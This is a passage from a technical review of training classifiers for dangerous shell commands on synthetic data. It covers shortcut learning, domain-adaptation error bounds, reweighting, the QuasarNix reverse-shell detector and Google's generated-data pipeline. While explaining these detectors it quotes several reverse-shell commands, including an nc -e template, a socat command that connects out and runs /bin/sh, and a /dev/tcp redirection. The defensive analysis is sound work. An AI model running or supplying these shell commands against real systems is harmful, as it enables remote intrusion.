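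*Disentangling Spurious Correlations* (Grunenwald, Crabbé and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes three mechanisms that can create a shortcut. First, the label itself can produce the feature, as when a developer sends only the dangerous class through a generator. Second, a hidden common cause can influence both the label and the feature. For example, commands from a security team's practice machines may be mostly attacks and also contain those machines' names. Third, selection can link the label and the feature. If a developer keeps dangerous commands that matched a keyword list and harmless ones that didn't, the keywords predict the label better in the dataset than in the logs. In the paper's tests on reviews, news articles and film plots, models trained in the ordinary way relied on shortcuts of all three kinds.

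They also tested a remedy, invariant risk minimisation, which divides the training data into groups and penalises features whose relation to the label varies between groups. When the researchers reversed the shortcut in the test data, this method beat ordinary training in all nine comparisons, by 6.9 to 58.1 percentage points. When the shortcut still held, it did 2.2 to 11.7 points worse. The method needs groups in which the shortcut's strength differs, and it does not differ if all the dangerous commands in every group come from a generator.

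Image recognition provides a close parallel to the worked example. *Breaking the Synthetic-Real Domain Shortcut for Training-Free Generative Replay-based Class Incremental Learning* (2026) describes a model trained on real photographs of new categories and generated images of old ones. The model then assigned real photographs of the old categories to the new ones. It could still tell categories apart when it chose only among those learned at the same stage, so it had not forgotten them. The difference between real and generated images affected its predictions more than the difference between categories, much as the look matters more than the verb in the worked example.

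This can happen without synthetic data. In *AI for radiographic COVID-19 detection selects shortcuts over signal*, DeGrave, Janizek and Lee (2020) found that systems for detecting the disease in chest X-rays relied on confounding features rather than signs of illness. The systems seemed accurate but failed in new hospitals, and the researchers traced the problem to how developers had assembled the training images. They also warn that good results on outside data don't prove a model is free of shortcuts. The same applies to command classifiers if the outside data repeats the same link between source and label.

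The worked example assumes a classifier that weighs evidence perfectly, and real networks may do worse. *On the Foundations of Shortcut Learning* (2023) distinguishes how well a feature predicts the label from how readily a model picks it up, or its availability. Nonlinear models favoured available features more than linear models did, and this bias increased with depth. If a placeholder path is easier to learn than the many ways of destroying data, a deep network might keep relying on the path even when *q* is well above 2.2%.

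However, a classifier does not always use a mark that it could use. *When a Data Artifact Isn't a Shortcut* (2026) examined synthetic data for training language models by reinforcement learning. A separate classifier found a real statistical sign of which items were authentic, but the trained model did not measurably rely on it. A developer who can tell generated commands from natural ones should therefore suspect a shortcut and test for it, for instance by removing the mark and checking whether the verdicts change.

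### A bound for weighted mixtures

Ben-David, Blitzer and colleagues (2009), in *A theory of learning from different domains*, asked how to combine plentiful data of the wrong kind with scarce data of the right kind. They call the plentiful data the source and the data the classifier will face the target. For commands, these correspond to synthetic and natural examples. Training minimises α times the average error on natural examples plus (1 − α) times the average error on synthetic ones. With probability at least 1 − δ, the trained classifier *ĥ* satisfies

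err(*ĥ*) ≤ err(*h*₀) + 4KC + 2(1 − α)(½div + U + λ),

where err is the error rate on natural commands. The other terms are as follows.

| Term | Meaning |
|---|---|
| err(*h*₀) | The lowest error on natural commands that any classifier of the chosen type can reach |
| K = √(α²/β + (1 − α)²/(1 − β)) | The cost of uneven weights, where β is the natural share of the training set |
| C = √((2*d* log(2(*m* + 1)) + 2 log(8/δ))/*m*) | Sampling error with *m* labelled examples and a classifier type of complexity *d* |
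| div | The measured difference between natural and synthetic inputs, from 0 to 2 |
| U = 4√((2*d* log(2*m*′) + log(8/δ))/*m*′) | Uncertainty in div when it comes from *m*′ unlabelled commands of each kind |
| λ | The lowest total error, natural plus synthetic, of any single classifier of the chosen type |

The complexity *d* is the VC dimension, the largest number of examples that classifiers of this type can label in every possible way. K equals one if every example counts equally (α = β) and grows as the weights become uneven. If 100 of 10,000 examples are natural commands and together receive half the total weight, K is about 5.

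The divergence div measures how much more often a pair of classifiers of the chosen type can disagree on one kind of input than on the other. Ben-David and colleagues approximate it by training a classifier to tell the two kinds apart. If that classifier's average error is *e*, the estimate is 2(1 − 2*e*), so perfect separation gives 2 and random guessing gives 0. This estimate needs no danger labels, but λ does, because it measures whether one rule can classify both kinds of data correctly. λ will be large if the generated data reflects a different standard of danger from the operators'.

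More synthetic data reduces C by increasing *m*. But if every example counts equally, it also lowers α, which gives more weight to the mismatch, ½div + U + λ. Extra synthetic data can only help when the mismatch is close to zero, but when the mismatch is large, synthetic data is worth using under the bound only while natural data is scarce. Once there are more than about *d*/(mismatch)² natural examples, the best α is one, which means ignoring the synthetic data entirely. With *d* = 1,601 and a mismatch of 0.715, values close to those in the researchers' experiment on product reviews, this threshold is about 3,130 natural examples.

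That limit would be a poor guide for commands. At the rate of Huawei's blocked class, 3,130 natural commands would include about nine blocked ones, too few to justify discarding the generated examples. The bound concerns the overall error rate and treats all examples alike. If one command in a thousand is dangerous, a classifier that flags nothing has an error rate of only 0.1% but misses every dangerous command.

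The bound is also loose. The same paper gives a simpler version for training on source data alone. With unlimited data, this version limits the target error to the source error plus ½div plus λ. If the source is the worked example's original training set and the target is natural commands with equal classes, these three terms are 7.5%, 42.5% and 25%. The bound therefore guarantees only that the error on natural commands is below 75%, while the actual error is 50%. Ben-David and colleagues make no claim about the bound's exact values. In their review experiments, the bound matched the shape of the error curves, and the α that minimised it gave low error. The bound is therefore a reasonable guide to which changes help, but it can't predict a classifier's miss rate.

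### How much synthetic data to add

Later work calculates the error itself in simpler settings, and it is more favourable to imperfect data. Jain, Montanari and Sasoglu (2024), in *Scaling laws for learning with real and surrogate data*, use "surrogate" for any data from a cheaper source than the real one, including synthetic data. Their simplest case is estimating the averages of *d* quantities from *n* real and *m* surrogate examples, where the noise in each quantity has variance one and Δ² is the squared distance between the real and surrogate averages. If every example counts equally, the expected error is

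(*m*/(*n* + *m*))² Δ² + *d*/(*n* + *m*).

As *m* grows, the noise disappears but the error approaches Δ², as if the developer had never collected any real data. With the best possible weight on the surrogate data, the error is instead

(*d*/*n*) × (Δ² + *d*/*m*)/(Δ² + *d*/*m* + *d*/*n*).

The second factor is always below one, so well-weighted surrogate data helps a little however different it is from the real data. For example, suppose 10 quantities are estimated from 100 real examples and 900 surrogate ones, with Δ² = 0.5. Using only the real data gives an error of 0.1. Pooling all the examples equally gives the surrogate data 90% of the weight and raises the error to 0.415, about four times as high. Reducing that weight to 16% lowers the error to 0.084.

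This seems to contradict the advice of Ben-David and colleagues to ignore source data beyond a certain point. They choose the weight α to minimise an upper limit on the error, which can mean discarding data that would have helped slightly. In practice, the gain from keeping that data may be too small to matter, and the best weight isn't known in advance. Jain and colleagues choose it by testing on held-out real data. For a command classifier, that test set would need natural dangerous commands, which are the examples that are missing.

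In *Learning with Synthetic Data via SGD in High-Dimensional Linear Regression* (2026), a fixed synthetic share *p* leaves an error proportional to *p*² times the mismatch, even with unlimited data. Halving the synthetic share would cut that error to a quarter.

Shidani, Farghly and colleagues (2025), in *Beyond Real Data*, derive a best ratio of synthetic to real data that depends on how different the two are. Error rises on either side of that ratio, and they observed the same pattern on photographs and brain scans. Kua and Song (2026), in *Generative Data Augmentation Without External Data*, point out that the gain from synthetic data can't exceed the gap between the classifier trained on real data and the best classifier of its type. In their image experiments, cropping, rotating and otherwise transforming real pictures also achieved most of the largest gains. However, their generators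 learned only from the classifier's own training set, whereas a language model that writes commands brings in outside knowledge.

Unlike these results, *When Does Synthetic Data Augmentation Improve Score-Based Imbalanced Classification?* (Ma, Lyu and Zhang, 2026) treats the dangerous class separately. In its setting, which is the closest to command safety, a developer has natural examples of both classes and adds synthetic ones only to the rare class. The paper distinguishes two easily confused effects of adding these examples: they give the rare class more weight in training, and they change what that class looks like.

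If the classifier is flexible enough to represent the correct ranking of commands, the extra weight has no lasting benefit. It raises all the scores but leaves their order unchanged. Apart from constants and a logarithm, their bound on how far AUC falls below the best possible value is

√(*k*/(*n* + *s*)) + (*s*/(*n* + *s*)) W,

where *n* is the number of natural examples, *s* the number of synthetic ones and *k* the number of parameters. W is the Wasserstein distance between synthetic and natural examples of the rare class, roughly the average distance one would have to move the synthetic examples to make them match the natural ones.

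Huawei's dataset has only about 140 commands in the blocked class, so balancing that class against the rest would take nearly 47,000 synthetic commands. This would reduce the square-root term by about 29% but add roughly half of W to the bound. The estimate is only a rough guide because it omits constants, but it suggests that full balance is worthwhile only if the generator is very good or the classifier badly needs more data.

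When dangerous commands are very rare, synthetic data can do more for a classifier that is too simple to represent the correct ranking. Shifting the class balance may give the classifier an easier target and improve its ranking, which changing the threshold cannot do. A developer can get the same shift without introducing a mismatch by giving each natural dangerous command more weight, but a few unusual commands then have a large influence.

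### Importance weighting and its limits

Importance weighting tries to correct the mixture by giving each training example with features *x* the weight p_use(*x*)/p_train(*x*). If `find` commands make up 60% of the training set and 6% of production, each counts a tenth as much. The weighted training error then equals, on average, the error in use. This requires that the relationship between features and label is the same in training and in use, and that everything found in use also appears in training.

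The worked example violates the condition on labels. Commands that have a destructive verb and don't look generated make up 8.75% of its first training set but 42.75% of natural commands (again with equal classes), so each receives a weight of about 4.9. This weight multiplies the dangerous and harmless examples in that group equally, so the odds of danger remain 0.84 and the classifier still allows those commands.

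Weights that also depend on the label would work. A generated dangerous command without the look would count 0.95/0.10 = 9.5 times and one with the look 0.05/0.90 = 0.056 times, which would make the look as rare among dangerous commands as it is in real use. But the developer needs to know how often natural dangerous commands have the look to calculate these weights. The weighting also makes the data less informative. Of 1,000 generated dangerous commands, the 100 without the look would carry 95% of the weight, and the set would be about as informative as 111 equally weighted examples. *Mandoline* (2021) describes the same loss when two datasets barely overlap and a few examples receive very high weights.

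Weighting cannot help with cases that are missing from the training data. PocketOS's agent deleted a database with a `curl` request containing `volumeDelete`. If a generator never produces deletions made through web requests, the training set has no such examples to weight. Fang, Lu and colleagues (2023), in *Generalizing Importance Weighting to A Universal Solver for Distribution Shift Problems*, handle this problem by weighting the cases that the training data covers and learning the rest directly from validation data. In effect, this means obtaining labelled natural examples of whatever the generator missed.

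Odunlami, Riedlinger and Gottschalk (2026), in *When Does Training on Synthetic Data Provably Work?*, show how badly a classifier can perform in the uncovered region. They generated counterparts to real photographs of big cats and bears, then trained a classifier with correct labels for the generated images and reversed labels for the real ones. Its error was 0.5% on generated images and 99.25% on real ones, so a good synthetic score can't rule out near-total failure. Ordinary training did not produce anything like this. Across 90 network designs trained only on generated images, those with lower error on generated images also tended to have lower error on real ones, with a squared correlation of up to 0.92. This is encouraging, but every category in the training set was generated, so the networks could not use an image's source to predict its label. The result is therefore much weaker evidence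 about datasets in which only the dangerous class is synthetic.

Once a large network fits all its training examples, giving some examples more weight than others may have no effect. *Is Importance Weighting Incompatible with Interpolating Classifiers?* (2021) explains this for cross-entropy, the usual training objective for classifiers. A different objective restores the effect. If a developer adds weights and gets the same classifier, that doesn't show the mixture was harmless.

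### Correcting for a changed base rate

If the only difference between training and use is how common dangerous commands are, the correction is simple. Let π be the dangerous share in use and π₀ the share in training. Bayes' rule gives

log-odds in use = log-odds in training + log [π/(1 − π)] − log [π₀/(1 − π₀)].

For a balanced training set and one dangerous command in a thousand, this correction subtracts 6.9 from every score. The order of the commands doesn't change, but the scores can then be used as probabilities. In the worked example every score falls below zero, so a classifier that treated both kinds of error as equally bad would flag nothing. A team that considers a miss 1,000 times as bad as a false alarm should lower its threshold by 6.9, which almost exactly cancels the correction.

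Lipton, Wang and Smola (2018), in *Detecting and Correcting for Label Shift with Black Box Predictors*, call a pure change of base rate label shift. The formula is valid only for label shift, but generating only the dangerous class also changes what dangerous commands look like. After the correction, the worked example's original classifier gives a command with both the verb and the look a 12.6% chance of being dangerous, and a command with the verb alone a 0.08% chance. The true figure for natural commands is 0.8% in both cases, so the first estimate is about sixteen times too high and the second is nearly ten times too low.

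Lipton and colleagues also estimate an unknown base rate from a classifier's verdicts on unlabelled data. With two classes, the estimate is

π = (share flagged in use − false-alarm rate)/(recall − false-alarm rate),

using the recall and false-alarm rate from held-out data. The worked example's original classifier flags 5% of natural commands whether they are dangerous or not, and its held-out false-alarm rate is also 5%. The estimated base rate is therefore zero, however many dangerous commands the logs contain.

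## Detectors trained on generated attacks and real background commands

The worked example assumed that most generated commands are recognisable as generated. How recognisable they are depends on whether the developer uses expert templates, a grammar or a language model. QuasarNix, a reverse-shell detector, is an example of the riskiest mixture, in which every attack is synthetic and every harmless command is natural.

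### Templates, grammars and language models

A template is a command with placeholders. One of QuasarNix's templates is `nc -e SHELL IP_A PORT_NR`, and filling in a shell, an address and a port produces a command that opens a reverse shell. An expert writes the template once, and a program can then generate thousands of variants with the same label.

Labeling every command generated from a template as dangerous is reliable only if the danger lies in the template's fixed part. A reverse shell is still a reverse shell whichever address fills the gap. But whether `rm -r PATH` clears a cache or destroys a database depends on the path, so a program that fills the gap at random and labels every result dangerous will mislabel many of them. Templates are therefore better suited to generating intrusions than operators' mistakes.

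A grammar is a set of rules for building valid commands. Ragsdale and Boppana wrote 6,222 rules for 86 Linux programs from the programs' manual pages. They compared this method with one that draws arguments from a pool shared by all the programs and often produces errors. For example, `--output=source` is valid for `df`, which reports disk space, but not for `grep`, which searches text.

Their system, ShIOEnv, also measures how many of a command's arguments matter. It runs the command, removes some arguments, runs it again and compares the results. The score is the share of shortened versions that behave differently, with each version weighted by the number of arguments it keeps. In `uname -a -s -r`, which prints system details, `-a` makes the other two options redundant. The three shortened versions that keep `-a` behave like the original and have a total weight of 5. The other four behave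 differently and have a total weight of 4, so the score is 4/9, or 0.44. About 59% of the grammar's commands scored above 0.5, compared with 25% of those from the shared pool.

The researchers then trained small language models to predict what a command would print and change, and tested them on 357 commands from honeypot logs. The model trained on the grammar's commands was exactly right 45.7% of the time, compared with 33.3% for the model trained on the shared pool and 24.1% for the one trained on commands adapted from NL2CMD. Predicting a command's effects is a different task from judging its danger, but the test commands came from attackers.

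Commands can be valid and informative without being realistic, because real operators add redundant options and make typing errors. NL2CMD's generator discards commands that fail, so it would have discarded a typo like Huawei's `xrgs kill`. Ragsdale and Boppana recommend keeping some low-scoring commands in data meant for deployment, because these may represent common behaviour. Their warning about what the dataset can't show also means that developers can't use the dataset to estimate the base rate, or to choose an alarm threshold that depends on that rate. The dataset covers only 86 programs, which include `rm`, `shred` and `curl` but not `kill`, `git` or `terraform`.

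A language model can write whole commands without a rule for each program. *CmdCaliper* (Huang, Yang and colleagues, 2024) used several models to produce 28,520 pairs of similar commands to train a system that measures similarity. This approach extends quickly to new programs, but it doesn't guarantee that the commands are valid or varied. Google's method adds some control by giving the model a taxonomy of attacks and having a critic check the output.

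### Defects that reveal the generator

Some generated commands can't run. The QuasarNix team checked the syntax of 9,531 generated attacks and found that 99.13% were valid. All 83 errors were in Perl commands, because the generator sometimes started variable names with a digit, which Perl doesn't allow. Language models can make syntax errors more often. In *Towards Automated Pentesting with Large Language Models* (2026), 90% of the generated samples of PowerShell, Microsoft's command language, parsed without errors.

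An invalid command can be an acceptable training example, since real logs contain plenty of them. But a generator tends to repeat the same error, and if it writes only the attacks, that error becomes a sign of attack in the training data.

Repeated or implausible values cause the same problem. *LLM-Generated Samples for Android Malware Detection* (2025) used GPT-4.1-mini to write records of malicious apps. Some records shared a hash, a file fingerprint that should be unique, and some hashes contained suspicious runs of zeros. A few records also lacked the label that all of them should have had. According to the paper, these defects didn't affect its results, but a pipeline that read labels from the model's output would have had to fill in the missing ones.

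In the worst case, the mark that distinguishes generated attacks is in both the training and the test data. *Beyond Heavy Log Curation* (2026) describes this problem in ATLAS, a dataset of logs from simulated attacks. Every malicious entry contains at least one of three strings, such as `payload.exe`, and the same strings appear in all ten parts of the dataset. A detector could memorise them and get a perfect score. When the researchers replicated an earlier detector, they replaced the strings in the training data and left the originals in the test data. This precaution takes little work, but someone has to notice the strings first.

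### How QuasarNix builds its dataset

Trizna, Demetrio and colleagues (2024), in *Robust Synthetic Data-Driven Detection of Living-Off-the-Land Reverse Shells*, set out to detect attacks that use programs already installed on the victim's machine. They generate attacks from templates with seven kinds of gap: the shell, network protocol, address, port, temporary file, variable name and file descriptor (a number that identifies an open file or connection). The values that fill these gaps come from the defended company's logs, expert lists or a random generator. Values from the logs make the attacks look more like the company's ordinary commands, so a detector is less likely to identify them by unfamiliar paths.

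The harmless commands came from a network of about 50,000 Linux machines that produces around 12 million events a day. Two hours of logs supplied about 266,000 distinct commands for training, and another two hours, a month later, supplied about 235,000 for testing. The month-long gap is a strength because it tests whether the detector still works after the company's activity has changed. But two-hour samples probably miss many jobs that run overnight or once a week. Because duplicates were removed, a command run 10,000 times counts the same as a command run once, so the false-alarm rate measures the share of distinct harmless commands flagged, not the share of events.

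The team randomly assigned 70% of the templates to training and 30% to testing, then generated as many attacks as there were harmless commands in each set. Their main classifier used gradient-boosted trees, a method that adds the outputs of many small decision trees. Its input records which words and punctuation marks appear in a command but not their order.

The same kind of classifier was trained on three versions of the attack data, and detection was measured at one false alarm per 100,000 harmless commands.

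| Attacks in the training data | Share of test attacks detected |
|---|---|
| Many generated variants of each template | 99.94% |
| One standard example of each template | 7.12% |
| The same standard examples, repeated until the classes were equal | 7.75% |

Repeating the examples barely helped, so the benefit came from variety rather than class balance. This agrees with the theoretical result that weighting the rare class more heavily does little for a flexible classifier.

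However, the 99.94% is a detection rate for new templates filled in by the same program, and the test set contained no attacks recorded during real intrusions. Only the first classifier was trained on the generator's range of addresses, paths and variable names, which may explain part of its advantage. A collection of existing detection rules caught only 3.37% of the same attacks. Trizna and colleagues take this as evidence that the rules are too rigid, but the rate would also be low if the generated attacks differed from the real attacks the rules were written to catch. The experiment can't separate these explanations.

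The paper gives conflicting AUC values for the two classifiers trained without generated variants. Its text reports 0.844 for the classifier trained on standard examples and 0.808 for the one trained on repeated examples, while its results table reports 95.63% and 75.22%. Both classifiers have low detection rates whichever values are correct. If the table is right, the classifier trained on standard examples ranked most attacks above most harmless commands and failed mainly at the strict threshold, but its ranking was much weaker if the text is right.

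### A harder test two years later

In May 2026 the team published a journal version, *Robust Large-Scale Detection of Living-Off-the-Land Reverse Shells via Data Synthesis*, which replaces the random split with 11 distinct test templates chosen by hand. Some templates are nearly identical, so a random split could put one in training and its near-copy in the test. Two PHP templates, for instance, differ only in the function that starts the shell. Four of the 11 test templates use programs that never appear in the training attacks. The team also repeated the generation and training ten times.

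The boosted trees now detected 60.2% of attacks on average, with a standard deviation of 8.2 points, at one false alarm per million. A convolutional network averaged 46.4%, but its standard deviation was 32.7 points, so a single training run could produce a good detector or a nearly useless one.

Comparing 60.2% with the earlier 99.94% exaggerates the decline, because the permitted false-alarm rate for the 60.2% result is ten times lower. The first paper reports 96.93% at one false alarm per million, but the journal version gives the same figure for one per 100,000.

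Overall accuracy is a better comparison because it doesn't depend on that choice. It fell from 99.98% to 90.84%. Since the classes are equal in size, the new accuracy and an F1 of 89.92% imply that the classifier missed about 18% of attacks and raised almost no false alarms. The earlier classifier could have missed at most about 0.04% of attacks. The harder split is the most likely reason for the drop, although the two papers also differ somewhat in how they describe the way the gaps were filled.

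The trees missed some kinds of attack far more often than others. In a breakdown of 29,997 test attacks, they caught 98.5% of those that named an interpreter such as `python` or `php`. The overall rate in that breakdown was 67.6%, so they caught only about half of the rest. Trizna and colleagues deliberately kept `awk` and `zsh` out of the training attacks, and report that attacks using them were harder to detect.

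The test set has about 235,000 attacks, but they come from 11 templates, each supplying roughly 9% of the total, so replacing two or three templates could change the result considerably. The ten repetitions don't measure this uncertainty because they all used the same test set.

The reported false-alarm rate of one per million is also uncertain, because the test included only 235,000 harmless commands. A single false alarm among them would be a rate of about four per million, so the researchers must have set the threshold above the score of every harmless command in the test. The true rate could still be as high as 13 per million, using a 95% confidence limit. At that rate, the network's 12 million daily events would produce about 150 false alarms a day instead of 12.

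### What the classifier relied on

The team used SHAP, which divides a classifier's score among the parts of its input, to find which features mattered. The dot was the strongest sign of an attack, with an average contribution of 3.05, followed by the number `10` at 0.88. The number `127` was also in the top ten. All three are common in network addresses, which the classifier receives as sets of numbers and dots (`10.1.1.2`, for example, is split this way). The signs of harmlessness included `lib`, `memory` and `proc`, which come from paths that were common on this company's machines, such as `/sys/fs/cgroup/memory/memory.stat`.

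Trizna and colleagues regard these features as consistent with expert knowledge. They are partly right, because a reverse shell has to connect to something and usually contains an address. But dots also occur in file names, version numbers and many harmless network commands. The case for the two numbers is weaker. Addresses that begin with 10 belong to private networks, and a machine uses `127.0.0.1` to refer to itself. An attacker elsewhere on the internet would normally use neither, although one already inside the network might use the first. The importance of `127`, at least, probably reflects the generator's choice of values.

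According to the journal version, the training attacks contain 220,526 different addresses but only two different ports, even though the described method can choose any port from 0 to 65535. A classifier could easily use those two ports to recognize attacks. Neither port seems to be among the ten strongest signs of attack, so there is no evidence that this classifier did.

The team also compared the vocabularies of the two classes. Of the words and symbols the classifier can recognise, 1,489 appear in both classes and only 109 appear in attacks alone. The researchers argue that this overlap makes false correlations less likely. But another 2,496 appear only in the natural commands, so every training command that contains one of them is labelled harmless. Filling templates with local values made the attacks resemble the company's commands but did not give them the same variety.

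The two classes may also differ in how they reached the dataset. The natural commands came through Linux's audit system, which records a program and its arguments after the shell has processed any redirection of input or output. Several attack templates contain redirections that this system would not record as part of the command. The symbol `>&`, which redirects output, is among the ten strongest signs of attack, so it may help the classifier distinguish commands that somebody wrote from commands that a logger captured. According to the journal version, some logging tools reduce one common kind of reverse shell to `/bin/bash -i`. A real attack logged this way would lack the features the classifier had learned to look for.

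### Tests with altered attacks

The researchers also changed the text of the test attacks without changing their effect, assuming an attacker who could not see the detector's scores. The boosted trees kept an accuracy of at least 93% against one family of alterations, but both the trees and the convolutional network failed completely against another family applied at full strength. Since only the text had changed, these failures are strong evidence that the classifiers depended on surface features.

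Adding altered attacks to the training data restored detection of the alterations the team tested and changed which features the trees relied on. The strongest feature was now `proc`, which lowered the score by 3.22 on average, and the dot mattered much less. Trizna and colleagues conclude that the new classifier had learned the organisation's normal activity better and no longer used shortcuts.

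The first half of that conclusion is more convincing than the second. Every Linux machine has a `/proc` directory, but how often its name appears in commands depends on the monitoring tools and scripts in use. In this training set, `proc` separates natural commands from generated ones, but it may be a less useful feature outside the company that supplied the logs.

### Using the detector in another organisation

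The page accompanying the released models, *Living-off-The-Land Reverse-Shell Detection by Informed Data Augmentation* (2024), describes them as generally applicable and suitable for a wide variety of monitoring systems. Neither paper reports a test on a second organisation's logs, so performance there can only be inferred, and the models' features give reasons for caution. A company whose operators often type commands such as `ping 10.2.0.7` could see many more false alarms. So could a company whose routine commands rarely contain `lib`, `memory` or `proc`, because fewer of its harmless commands would have the words that lower the score. The original alarm threshold would probably be wrong as well.

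Retraining on the new organisation's logs should help, and the method requires it. But simply combining those logs with the released attacks could strengthen the shortcut. Some of the paths and variable names in the attacks came from the first company, so in the new mixture they would appear almost exclusively in attacks. The researchers added these values to hide which commands were generated, but a detector could now use them to identify those commands.

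A safer approach is to use the released code to generate new attacks with local values and pass them through the same logging steps as the natural commands. The worked example also suggests generating harmless commands that contain addresses, redirections and scripts, so that these features no longer identify a command's source. Somebody would still have to test the retrained detector on recorded intrusions to learn whether it catches real ones.

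## Adding real commands and investigated alerts to the training set

Google took a classifier trained on generated commands and tested it on a year of real security investigations, where it did well. It did better still when the developers added analysts' verdicts to the training data. Sophos, a security company, greatly improved its classifier by adding unusual harmless commands from its customers' machines. Both companies were trying to detect attacks rather than operators' mistakes.

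### How Google generates its examples

The Google system that Momeni and colleagues describe filters logs with loose rules written in YARA, a pattern-matching tool popular with malware researchers. Separate classifiers then check the matches for reverse shells, known hacking tools, and the abuse of programs already on the machine. Patterns alone are not enough because one that looks for a hacking tool's name can also match harmless commands. Hydra, for example, is both a password cracker and a framework for configuring Python programs, and `man hydra` only opens a manual page.

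The training examples come from Simula, Google's generator. An analyst describes the task, and a language model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, breaks it down into taxonomies, or trees of increasingly specific categories. The reverse-shell taxonomy covers attack techniques and the programs an attacker might use, such as Bash, Python and Socat. Another taxonomy covers legitimate administration, networking and scripting. Simula picks a combination of categories, and the model turns it into a written scenario and then a command. In one scenario, Socat connects to a remote machine and starts a shell, and the model writes `socat TCP:10.0.0.5:4444 EXEC:'/bin/sh'`. In another, about network diagnostics, it writes `socat TCP-LISTEN:8080,fork STDOUT`, which uses the same program but starts no shell.

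Simula then prompts a critic, also a language model, with two separate questions about each command: whether it is a plausible example of its category, and whether it is not. It keeps the command only if both answers imply that it is plausible. Using both questions helps because language models tend to give whichever answer a question suggests.

Davidson, Seguin and colleagues (2026), in *Reasoning-Driven Synthetic Data Generation and Evaluation*, tested these steps on subjects such as mathematics, law and cyber threats. If a share μ of the generated answers is correct, and the critic accepts a share *a* of the correct answers and *b* of the wrong ones, the accuracy after filtering is

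μ*a*/(μ*a* + (1 − μ)*b*).

For example, if 90% of the answers are correct and the critic accepts 95% of those but only 30% of the wrong ones, about 97% of the accepted answers are correct. In the mathematics tests, the critic was less effective on the model's own errors than on errors that the researchers had planted. It may therefore also be less effective on a command generator's errors, which are not planted.

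The taxonomies covered 74% to 78% of the categories in taxonomies written by experts, compared with 50% to 52% when the model expanded each category in a single attempt. Simula will generate few or no examples of a missing category, and the critic won't detect the gap because it only checks examples that were generated.

Results also depended on how well the model had learned the subject. The critic rejected 2% of the multiple-choice questions about cyber threats but 61% of those on law, where the model answered only 57% of real exam questions correctly. Reverse shells are probably a favourable subject because security websites document them in detail. A model has no comparable source of information on which of a company's directories are safe to delete.

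### Results on a year of investigations

Google's test commands came from a year of investigation tickets. The dangerous ones came from verified incidents, and the harmless ones closely resembled attacks. The team verified all the labels after the investigations. This test is far more realistic than QuasarNix's, whose attacks all came from templates.

| Training data for the reverse-shell classifier | Dangerous examples | Harmless examples | Best F1 |
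|---|---|---|---|
| 100 generated commands | 50 | 50 | 0.83 |
| 1,000 generated commands | 500 | 500 | 0.93 |
| 20,000 generated commands | 10,000 | 10,000 | 0.95 |
| Set made by hand | 70 | 3,500 | 0.88 |

This is strong evidence that training on generated commands can carry over to real ones. The classifier reached an F1 of 0.95 on commands chosen to be difficult, which means its precision and recall were both at least 90%.

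Part of the explanation is probably that Simula generated both classes, so looking generated is a weaker clue to the class, as in the balanced version of the worked example. The classifier also replaces network addresses and numbers with placeholders before it counts word sequences. This removes the kind of feature that led QuasarNix to treat `10` and `127` as signs of attack.

Reverse shells also suit this method because many contain the same short sequence, such as `sh >& /dev/tcp/`. Mistaken deletions contain no such telltale sequence. Momeni and colleagues found that their word-sequence classifier did just as well as two neural models that convert a whole command into a list of numbers representing its meaning or form. They suggest that a telltale sequence stands out in a count but becomes harder to detect when a model summarises a long command.

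The generated set's advantage seems to come from its size and range. With 50 dangerous examples, it did worse than the handmade set with 70, although the handmade set also had many more harmless commands. Increasing the generated data from 1,000 commands to 20,000 added only 0.02 to F1. The expert who built the handmade set drew on web searches and threat reports as well as logs, so the comparison is not between synthetic and natural data.

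The scores somewhat overstate deployed performance because each is the best F1 at any threshold on the test set, and a deployed classifier has to fix its threshold in advance. Some of the attacks in real logs are also staged. One reverse shell that Momeni and colleagues give as an example has `ktd-test-reverse-shell` in its name and matches a procedure in Google Cloud's *Testing Container Threat Detection*, a guide to checking that an alarm works. The procedure copies `echo`, which only prints text, to a file called `sh` and connects it to Google's public name server, so nobody gains control. An alarm is still the correct response, but the command comes from a public web page that the generating model may have seen in training, so it is easier to detect than an intruder who is trying to hide. If the verified incidents include many such tests, the scores overstate how well the classifier finds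 real intruders.

### Retraining on analysts' verdicts

In live use, analysts investigate the system's alerts, and their verdicts become new training examples. The system retrains daily on these examples and the original training set. To measure the benefit, the team ran two reverse-shell classifiers on a year of distinct commands from Google's logs. The fixed classifier was trained once. The updated one started with the same training set and had already learned from 180 days of verdicts when the comparison began.

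| | Fixed classifier | Updated classifier |
|---|---|---|
| True attacks found | 43 | 53 |
| False alarms | 107 | 30 |
| Precision | 28.7% | 63.9% |

The updated classifier found every attack that the fixed one found and ten more, with 72% fewer false alarms. Raising the fixed classifier's threshold could have reduced its false alarms but would not have found the ten extra attacks, so retraining must have improved how the classifier ranks commands.

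It could plausibly have done so in two ways. The classifier may have learned new forms of attack from the confirmed incidents, or it may have learned to give familiar harmless commands lower scores. Lower scores for harmless commands let the developers set a lower threshold for the same number of tickets and so catch more attacks. The experiment can't separate these effects. It is also unclear how varied the ten additional attacks were. The commands were distinct, but Google Cloud's test procedure puts the current time in the command, so each run of the same test would count as a distinct command.

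The fixed classifier's precision was only 29% on a year of logs, whereas its F1 of 0.95 on the ticket test set implies precision of at least 90%. The most likely reason is the difference in base rates. Verified incidents were presumably a sizeable share of the ticket test set, while attacks are extremely rare in a year of logs. The thresholds may have differed too. The F1 shows that the classifier can tell attacks from similar harmless commands, but the 29% better reflects what analysts would see.

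Momeni and colleagues also tracked the live system's precision from September 2023 to May 2025 and found that it generally improved across four types of detection. This is weaker evidence than the direct comparison, because other changes at Google could have contributed. The 20-month graph also contains few independent measurements, because each point covers the latest 100 investigations. At the reported ticket rates, that many investigations take about seven months for reverse shells and 15 months for hacking tools.

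### How much each verdict counts

A new verdict starts with a weight *w*, which falls steadily to zero over 180 days. After *a* days its weight is

*w*(1 − *a*/180),

so a verdict counts half as much after 90 days. The decay keeps the classifier from relying on outdated evidence, such as false alarms caused by a program that the company no longer uses.

The initial weight of analysts' verdicts was "1:1 with the synthetic data", which could refer to individual examples or to the totals. At about one ticket every two days and one verdict per ticket, analysts produce some 86 verdicts in 180 days. Because of the decay, these count as much as 43 new ones. If a new verdict has the same weight as one generated command, verdicts make up only about 0.2% of the total weight in a training set with 20,000 generated commands. If the ratio applies to the totals, a recent verdict counts as much as several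 hundred generated commands.

A high weight makes the classifier respond quickly, but it also increases the harm from a wrong verdict. Momeni and colleagues acknowledge that some verdicts are misleading. An analyst may escalate a ticket because of something else on the machine, or close it for a reason unrelated to the command.

Confirmed attacks and false alarms decay on the same schedule, which is probably not ideal. A company's harmless activity changes as its software changes, but an attacker can use the same reverse shell for years. If analysts confirm a rare technique only once, that example has no influence after six months, and the classifier must then rely on the generated commands to recognise it. A slower decay for confirmed attacks would avoid this with little downside, since there are so few of them.

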